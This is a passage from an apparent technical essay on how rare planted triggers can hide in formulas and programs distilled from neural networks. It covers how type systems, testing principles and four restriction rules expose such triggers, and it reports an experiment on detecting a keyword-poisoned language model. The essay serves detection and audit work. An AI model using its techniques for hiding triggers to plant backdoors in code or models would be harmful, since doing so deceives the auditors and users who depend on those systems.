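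Lazić and colleagues extended the method to some programs with arrays. Their example is a memory system that keeps three copies of everything and takes a majority vote when reading, so it can survive one fault. They checked every size up to 2 addresses and 11 data values and found no error. This result, together with their theorems, proves the system correct for every memory size and every type of data.

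In *Towards a small model theorem for data independent systems in Alloy*, Momtahan (2005) proves a similar theorem for Alloy, a tool that searches for counterexamples up to a size the user chooses. Normally, a search that finds none doesn't rule out larger counterexamples. For a data-independent type, the theorem gives a size beyond which enlarging the type produces no new counterexamples.

### The 0-1 principle

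Sorting needs order comparisons, so by the earlier count an auditor would need 75 tests for lists of length 4. But 16 are enough for a sorting network, which is made of comparators that each compare the values in two positions and put the smaller one first. The network can't use the result of a comparison for anything else, so every output is a combination of minimums and maximums.

The 0-1 principle is that a network sorts every input if it sorts every list of zeros and ones. There are 2^n such lists for n inputs (*The Zero-One Principle*, 2008). The inputs can be numbers, names or anything else with an order.

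For example, one four-input network compares positions 1 and 2, then 3 and 4, then 1 and 3, then 2 and 4, but lacks the final comparison of positions 2 and 3.

1. Given 5, 9, 2, 7, the network produces 2, 7, 5, 9. The 7 and the 5 are in the wrong order.
2. Replace every number above 5 with 1 and every other number with 0. The input becomes 0, 1, 0, 1.
3. This replacement never reverses an order, so taking a minimum or maximum before or after it gives the same result. The network's output must therefore be the old output with the same replacement, which is 0, 1, 0, 1.
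4. That output isn't sorted either, so one of the 16 tests exposes the fault.

The same argument works for any fault if the cut is placed between two outputs that are in the wrong order. Adding the missing comparison makes the network pass all 16 tests.

The argument also limits how rare a fault can be. Suppose a network fails on a list of zeros and ones that contains k ones. It then fails on every input whose k largest values are in those k positions. If the values are independent draws from the same distribution, and ties are negligible, the k largest are equally likely to be in any k positions. A faulty four-input network therefore fails on at least one input in 6, and a faulty 20-input network on at least one in 184,756.

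Allowing other operations can break the principle. With subtraction and constants, for instance, a program can again test whole numbers for equality, using max(1 − |x − a|, 0). Even without arithmetic, testing with only zeros and ones may not be enough. In *Much ado about two (pearl)*, Voigtländer (2008) studies networks that compute running totals using any operation that, like addition, allows regrouping. He uses parametricity to prove that three is the fewest values that suffice for testing these networks.

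### Types that measure distance

For models that do arithmetic on real numbers, a type can instead limit how much the output changes when an input changes. *Distance Makes the Types Grow Stronger* (Reed and Pierce, 2010) calls a function c-sensitive if it magnifies the distance between any two inputs by a factor of at most c. The function 3x + 2 is 3-sensitive, but x² isn't c-sensitive for any c because its slope grows without bound.

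The type checker in these languages computes a sensitivity from the program text, roughly by counting uses of each input. For example, x + x uses x twice, so it is 2-sensitive. The compiler therefore guarantees a bound on the program's slope for every input.

An exact comparison of real numbers has no finite sensitivity in Reed and Pierce's system. A c-sensitive function sends two real numbers at distance d to results at most c·d apart. Since "true" and "false" are infinitely far apart, a yes-or-no function with finite sensitivity must give every real number the same answer. Parametricity gives the same conclusion for an unknown type, although in their system the program can still do arithmetic.

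An equality test on real numbers has unbounded sensitivity even if it returns 1 and 0 instead of "true" and "false". In 3·x + 2 + (x = a), moving x from a to a point 0.001 away changes the test's value by 1, which requires a sensitivity of about 1,000, and smaller moves require higher sensitivities, without limit. A programmer can declare infinite sensitivity to x, which allows any function, but the declaration appears in the type, as "Eq X" does in Haskell.

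Some operations that use comparisons have finite sensitivity. A comparator, which puts two values in order, is 1-sensitive because the values are equal at the point where they swap. For example, the pairs (3, 3.1) and (3.2, 3.1) are 0.2 apart, and so are their sorted versions, (3, 3.1) and (3.1, 3.2). Sorting a whole list is also 1-sensitive. A language designer can therefore provide minimum, maximum and sorting while withholding comparison.

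An author can still add a narrow spike:

3·x + 2 + max(1 − K·|x − a|, 0)

The checker would give this formula a sensitivity of K + 3. For a spike one millionth of a unit wide, K is 2 million, so an auditor can see from the type that part of the formula is extremely steep. On whole numbers, where K = 1 is enough, the sensitivity is only 4.

Reed and Pierce designed their system for differential privacy, in which a data holder adds random noise to published statistics so that no one person's record noticeably affects them. They discuss a query that counts the patients who are over 40 and named John Doe. Although the query singles out one person, its sensitivity is 1, because adding or removing one record changes the count by at most 1. Multiplying the answer by 1,000 raises the sensitivity to 1,000, and the system then requires 1,000 times as much noise. The type limits how much a special case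 can change the result, but not how rare the special case is. The noise hides the special case here, but a model that gives exact answers has no such protection.

Sensitivity types can also track rounding. *Type-Based Approaches to Rounding Error Analysis* (2025) describes NumFuzz, a language that builds on Reed and Pierce's system and measures distance by relative error. Subtracting two nearly equal numbers can magnify relative error without limit, so no finite bound of this kind can cover the step (x + 2⁵²) − 2⁵², which hides the trigger in the 29-symbol formula.

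### Triggers in length and position

A polymorphic function can't look at the elements of a list, but it can count them. The length is an ordinary whole number, so the function can compare it with a constant or even hash it. A function that reverses every list except those with exactly 4,097 elements satisfies Wadler's theorem. An auditor has to test every length, which is feasible if the model accepts at most 10,000 elements, but not if it takes several long lists whose lengths can vary independently. Reed and Pierce's types also allow triggers based on length. In their system, lists of different lengths are infinitely far apart, so a finite sensitivity doesn't limit how differently a program treats them.

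A function's behavior can also depend on an element's position. For example, a function that is supposed to return a list unchanged could move element 17 to the front. If the list holds applications, someone who can arrange to be 17th would benefit, whatever their application contains. One test on a list whose elements are all different would reveal the move, but only for lists of that length.

Stricter type systems can close some of these gaps. Linear types require a program to use each piece of data exactly once, so it can't drop or copy elements. Ordered types also control the order of use. *Substructural Parametricity* (Aberlé, Martens and Pfenning, 2025) proves that exactly one function has the ordered type for joining two lists, and exactly one has the type for reversing a list. In each case the type specifies the function completely, so the function can't make an exception for lists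 of length 4,097 or for any other input.

### Escape hatches

These guarantees apply to idealised languages, and most real ones offer ways around them. Abadi and colleagues describe a function that returns true for the number 0 and false for every other value of any type. It requires type information at run time, which many languages provide. In Java, every object has an equals method, so a function that accepts any type of object can call it. Haskell has unsafeCoerce, which treats a value of one type as another without any check. Its Safe Haskell mode rejects code that imports this function.

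Computations that never finish cause a milder problem. Wadler shows that with unrestricted recursion, his theorem holds only if g never finishes when given an input that never finishes. *The Impact of seq on Free Theorems-Based Program Transformations* adds conditions for seq, a Haskell operation that forces the program to evaluate a value. With seq, a function from an arbitrary type to yes or no may hang when its input does, but it still can't return yes for one finished value and no for another.

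A declared equality test also may not behave like equality. Seidel and Voigtländer assume that it does, but they point out that Haskell doesn't check this. An author can define a new type of number whose equality test works normally, except that 2,718,281,828 doesn't equal itself. A correct, polymorphic program for removing duplicates will then leave repeated copies of that number in the list. The 15 tests for lists of length 4 would miss this unless they used that number. As with custom operators, an auditor therefore has to read the definition of equality for every type the model uses.

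## What a ban costs, and rules short of a ban

A restriction that keeps out planted exceptions also keeps out exceptions that belong in the model. The Gregorian calendar has one. A year is a leap year if it is divisible by 4, except that a century year must also be divisible by 400. With remainders and an equality test, the number of days in year y is

365 + (y mod 4 = 0) − (y mod 100 = 0) + (y mod 400 = 0)

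The formula has size 19 and works for every year. Like 3·x + 2 + (x = a), it combines a simple rule with a rare exception. The simple rule, a leap day every fourth year, is wrong in 3 years out of every 400 (2100, 2200 and 2300, for example), so ε is 0.75%.

Ordinary data may not show the exception. The simple leap-year rule is right for every year from 1901 to 2099, because the only century year in that range, 2000, was a leap year. Someone who fitted a formula to those 199 years would get the simple rule with no errors, and its first mistake would come in 2100. Microsoft Excel still accepts 29 February 1900 because its designers copied the mistake from an older spreadsheet, Lotus 1-2-3, for compatibility.

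### The calendar without remainders

With only PySR's default operations, a formula can't reproduce even the four-year leap-year cycle. A 30-symbol formula contains y at most 15 times, so it is a ratio of polynomials of degree at most 15. Unless it is constant, it equals 365 in at most 15 years and 366 in at most 15 others. If its output is rounded, it can switch between the two values at most 30 times, but 400 years of leap days require nearly 200 switches.

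A grammar that takes the year's bits as inputs does better. The last two bits, b₀ and b₁, are both 0 exactly when 4 divides the year, so (1 − b₀)·(1 − b₁) computes the simple rule with degree 2. But a low degree cap excludes the century exception. For 12-bit years (0 to 4095) and a cap of 4, the simple rule differs from the true calendar in 30 years. Every other function in the grammar differs from the simple rule on at least 1/16 of inputs, or 256 years, and so differs from the true calendar in at least 226. The simple rule is therefore the best model available, and it is wrong on exactly the 30 rare cases.

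If the grammar has equality tests but no remainders, the author can add the exceptions to the simple rule one at a time, as in − (y = 2100). Each exception takes four symbols. There are 63 exceptions from 1583 to 9999, so the list takes 252 symbols, and it fails in the year 10,100. Every entry is also an equality test, the operation a cautious designer would want to ban first. A reader would be much more likely to overlook a planted sixty-fourth entry than a fourth term in the original formula.

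### Other functions that need suspect operations

Banning an operation also rules out its ordinary uses. Looking up a price by product code means testing the code for equality with stored codes. Banks check an international account number (IBAN) by rewriting it as one long number and rejecting it unless it leaves remainder 1 when divided by 97. Describing waves and vibrating springs requires sine or cosine. Parity, which is 1 when an odd number of bits are on, is a polynomial of degree n for n bits. A degree cap of 4 therefore forbids the parity of five bits, even though it is 1 on half of all inputs and so is not a rare trigger.

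Safety cut-offs are designed to trigger rarely. A controller that switches off a heater above 90 degrees may run for years without doing so. The cut-off is a jump in the output, so a slope limit excludes it. If a search scores formulas on ordinary operating data, keeping the cut-off does not improve the score.

### What the network-to-code proposals allow

How much a ban limits useful programs in practice depends on how often they need the banned operations. Some evidence comes from attempts to replace neural networks with readable code. In *Provably safe systems*, Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) argue that powerful AI systems should run as code that carries a machine-checkable proof that it meets a specification. They expect neural networks to discover the algorithms but not to run them: "The black box helps for learning, not for execution." In their proposal, either a language model writes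 the code or another AI extracts it from a trained network. They don't specify any operations that the code must avoid.

Michaud, Liao and colleagues (2024), in *Opening the AI black box*, automated the extraction for small networks that read a list one item at a time and update an internal state. Their method, MIPS, trains a network until it makes no errors on the test data, then simplifies its weights. It converts the internal states to whole numbers or bits, tabulates how each state leads to the next, and searches for a short formula that reproduces the table. The whole-number formulas can use remainders, absolute values and an operation that gives 1 only at 0, which tests whether x equals a when applied to x − a. The programs for bits also use XOR and comparisons.

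MIPS solved 32 of the 62 tasks that remained after the team dropped those the network couldn't learn. Going by the task definitions, addition, subtraction and multiplication would be enough for 28 of the 32, since x + y − 2xy is XOR when x and y are bits. A ban on all other operations would rule out the other four, which are testing whether the last two numbers are equal, two tasks with absolute values, and adding modulo 3. The team wrote the task list by hand, so these counts don't measure how common such functions are. Having the right primitive also didn't guarantee success, because MIPS failed on adding modulo 4, 5, 6, 7 and 8.

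More recent work uses a wide range of output languages. *Weights to Code* (Zhang, Bi and colleagues, 2026) designs a transformer, the kind of network behind language models, whose parts each do one simple job, so that PySR can find a formula for each arithmetic part. *Discovering Interpretable Algorithms by Decompiling Transformers to RASP* (Huang, Bakalova and colleagues, 2026) translates ordinary small transformers into a language that mirrors their steps, then deletes the steps that hardly affect the output. In one case this cut the program from 16,201,616 lines to 3. *Explaining Attention with Program Synthesis* (Hayes, Li and Andreas, 2026) uses a language model to write programs that imitate attention heads, the parts of a transformer that select relevant words. *SymTorch* (Tan, Soubki and Cranmer, 2026) fits PySR formulas to the inputs and outputs of any part of a network.

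| Work | Operations in the output | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Michaud and colleagues | arithmetic, remainder, absolute value, equality with 0, bit logic | 32 of 62 tasks without error |
| Zhang and colleagues | +, −, ×, ÷; also max(x, 0) for nonlinear tasks; copying an earlier item, or the largest or smallest recent one | 20 of 24 whole-number tasks with accuracy 1.00 |
| Huang and colleagues | equality between items, arbitrary matrices, arbitrary functions of one position | 8 of 11 algorithmic tasks and 9 of 17 formal languages, at 90% agreement or better |
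| Hayes and colleagues | Python with numerical and language libraries | replacing a quarter of the heads raised perplexity (a measure of prediction error) by 16% on average, at best |
| Tan and colleagues | whatever the user picks | four force laws and the solutions of three physical equations |

Zhang and colleagues used the most restricted language in the table and got the best score, but they left out tasks that its operators can't express, such as detecting palindromes. To look up a value by its key, they had to add an equality test. Their network normally used its arithmetic parts to compute the larger of two numbers. When they removed those parts, it still produced the larger number by learning to copy it.

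Huang and colleagues accept a program as faithful if it matches the network on at least 90% of inputs. The simple leap-year rule matches the calendar in 99.25% of years, so it would pass.

### For and against restriction

Tegmark and Omohundro demand proofs because a computer has finitely many states, so a safety property that has no proof must be violated somewhere, and a capable adversary may well find the violation. Testing can't rule this out, and an adversary can fake evidence but can't produce a valid proof of something false. They expect that once training has found a good algorithm, code can replace the network without losing performance. Zhang and colleagues, by contrast, write that their design "intentionally trades expressivity for interpretability". Tan and colleagues regard some loss as a virtue. Newton's F = ma is useful partly because it leaves out drag and relativity, which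 would make it harder to read for little gain in accuracy.

Others doubt that the approach can work for the systems that matter. *On Controllability of AI* (2020) quotes the AI researcher Ben Goertzel, who is unconvinced that provably safe general AI is feasible. He argues that a proof would hold only within a mathematical model of the world, and that a design that satisfied it would probably need an infeasible amount of computation. Huang and colleagues think that parts of a language model might reduce to a simple program, but that the whole model is unlikely to because its training data varies so much.

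Some tasks may have no short program to find. In *Replicating and Extending Weight-Space Programming*, Goworek, Hickey and colleagues (2026) asked GPT-6 Astra, an OpenAI language model, to write the weights of a network that recognises handwritten digits, without training it or seeing any images. The results were right about 50% of the time, compared with 82% for matching each image to the average image of each digit and 97% for a trained network of the same shape. The lack of data put Astra at a disadvantage, but it did much better on Breakout, a simple video game that can be played well with a few explicit rules.

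A separate objection to any restriction is that a clean formula doesn't show that the network it approximates is also clean. Suppose a network computes 3x + 2 except at x = a, and someone distils it from a million random inputs. The sample will almost certainly miss a, and the result will be 3x + 2. Replacing the network with this formula removes the trigger, but if the network keeps running and the formula only serves as its explanation, the trigger is still there and the auditor has checked the wrong object. Replacement can also remove useful exceptions, because distillation drops a safety cut-off or the century exception in the leap-year rule just as readily.

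Most of the work above produces approximations. In Hayes and colleagues' experiments, perplexity had risen by 16% while three quarters of the heads were still neural. *Discovering Differences in Strategic Behavior Between Humans and LLMs* (2026) describes its readable programs as hypotheses supported by predictive fit, and analyses the simplest good ones instead of the best-fitting ones.

Goworek and colleagues had two AI models translate the weights of a Breakout network into Python that chose the same move as the network in all 49,189 game states tested. But Astra had written that network as a set of on-off switches, with only 815 of its 20,486 weights nonzero. Trained networks are much harder to read. The team also gave Astra the weights of two small language models, one of which had been trained to produce gibberish after a certain keyword. When the poisoned examples had been mixed in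 throughout training, Astra identified the poisoned model in all ten runs but never found the keyword.

### Four rules short of a ban

A designer who wants to keep the leap-year rule can restrict suspect operations instead of banning them. The table applies four such restrictions to the running example, to three other ways of writing a trigger, and to the calendar. K is a large constant in the narrow bump, and H is a one-way function in the hash test.

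| Model | Minimum share of data per condition | Written reason for each suspect operation | Solver-checkable grammar, with a reference | Alarm on rare outcomes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 3·x + 2 + (x = a) | rejected | author must explain a | solver finds a | warning when x = a |
| 3·x + 3 − (x > a) − (a > x) | accepted | author must explain a | solver finds a | no warning |
| 3·x + 2 + 1/(1 + K·(x − a)²) | accepted | accepted, unless long constants need a reason | not allowed | no warning |
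| 3·x + 2 + (H(x) = c) | rejected | author must explain H and c | not allowed | warning when H(x) = c |
| Leap-year rule | rejected if the minimum is above 0.25% | three reasons, all public | allowed | possible warnings in century years |

Software that grows decision trees often lets the user set a minimum number of data points per leaf. A designer could set a similar rule for formulas, requiring every condition to be true on at least 0.1% of the data and false on at least 0.1%. This rule rejects the condition x = a, but it can allow x > a and a > x. If a is 2,718,281,828, for example, the first is true for 37% of 32-bit inputs and the second for 63%, so both pass. A formula can then combine them to detect the single input x = a, where both are false.

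The designer can apply the minimum to every combination of outcomes that can occur. Sampling then works well, because 10,000 random draws miss a region that holds 0.1% of inputs only about once in 20,000 tries. But a formula that reads 32 yes-or-no features has over four billion combinations, nearly all of them rare, so this stricter version would also reject most harmless formulas. The leaf-depth check is less strict because it counts only the features tested along a path in the tree. An author who also supplies the data can defeat either version by including enough rows with x = a.

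A rule that asks for reasons requires the author to justify what they write. *Interpretable weight-space programming builds transparent transformers and brain encoding models* (2026) describes a similar rule. An AI agent may write constants and lookup tables directly into a network, and an auditing agent judges after each round whether a person could interpret the changes. For the calendar, the author would have to justify three remainders, which is easy, but if remainders were banned, they would have to justify 63 separate years.

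This rule depends on the list of suspect operations and on the reviewer. The bump uses only school arithmetic, so the list must also cover long constants. Counting the bits in each constant is one way to decide which ones need a reason. A false reason can be convincing: the lines planted in the Linux kernel looked like error checking, and an author could say that a is a reserved code. Requiring a precise claim, such as "adds 1 at x = a and nowhere else", helps because a solver can check it, and the reviewer then only has to decide whether the exception is legitimate.

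This works every time only if the formula stays within a grammar where the solver always reaches an answer. One such grammar is Presburger arithmetic, which has addition, comparisons and remainders by fixed numbers. It can express the leap-year rule and the formula that hides a in ten small remainders. It can also express a single update step in each of the 32 tasks that MIPS solved, including the four that a ban would lose. Since those tasks use lists of 10 or 20 items, a solver can write out the whole loop. Michaud and colleagues used the verification tool Dafny to prove that one program, which adds binary numbers, is correct for all binary numbers, though they had to do part of the work by hand.

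The grammar excludes products of two inputs, exponentials and sine, and therefore most of the physical laws that Tan and colleagues recovered. Checking a model with a solver also requires a trustworthy reference. If the reference is the simple leap-year rule, the solver will report the true calendar's treatment of 2100 as a violation. If the author of the model also writes the reference, the same trigger can be in both. Tegmark and Omohundro want humans to write the specifications, with AI assistance, but a person can also forget the century exception.

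An alarm works while the model runs. The designer records how often each condition is true on ordinary inputs, and the software raises a warning whenever a condition has an outcome that was rarer than, say, 1 in 10,000. With six conditions, false alarms then occur in at most about 6 runs out of 10,000, as long as the inputs stay similar. The designer doesn't need to know a in advance, so the alarm works even on the hash test. It misses the pair of comparisons for the same reason the minimum share does, unless the software tracks combinations. It also misses the bump, because that formula has no conditions.

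A trigger may do its damage in a single use, as with the Linux backdoor, so the software has to hold the output until someone has looked at the warning. That delay would be dangerous in a safety cut-off, where the controller has to switch the heater off as soon as it passes 90 degrees and send the warning afterwards. The designer therefore has to decide in advance, for each rare branch, whether the model should wait for someone to check the warning or act immediately.
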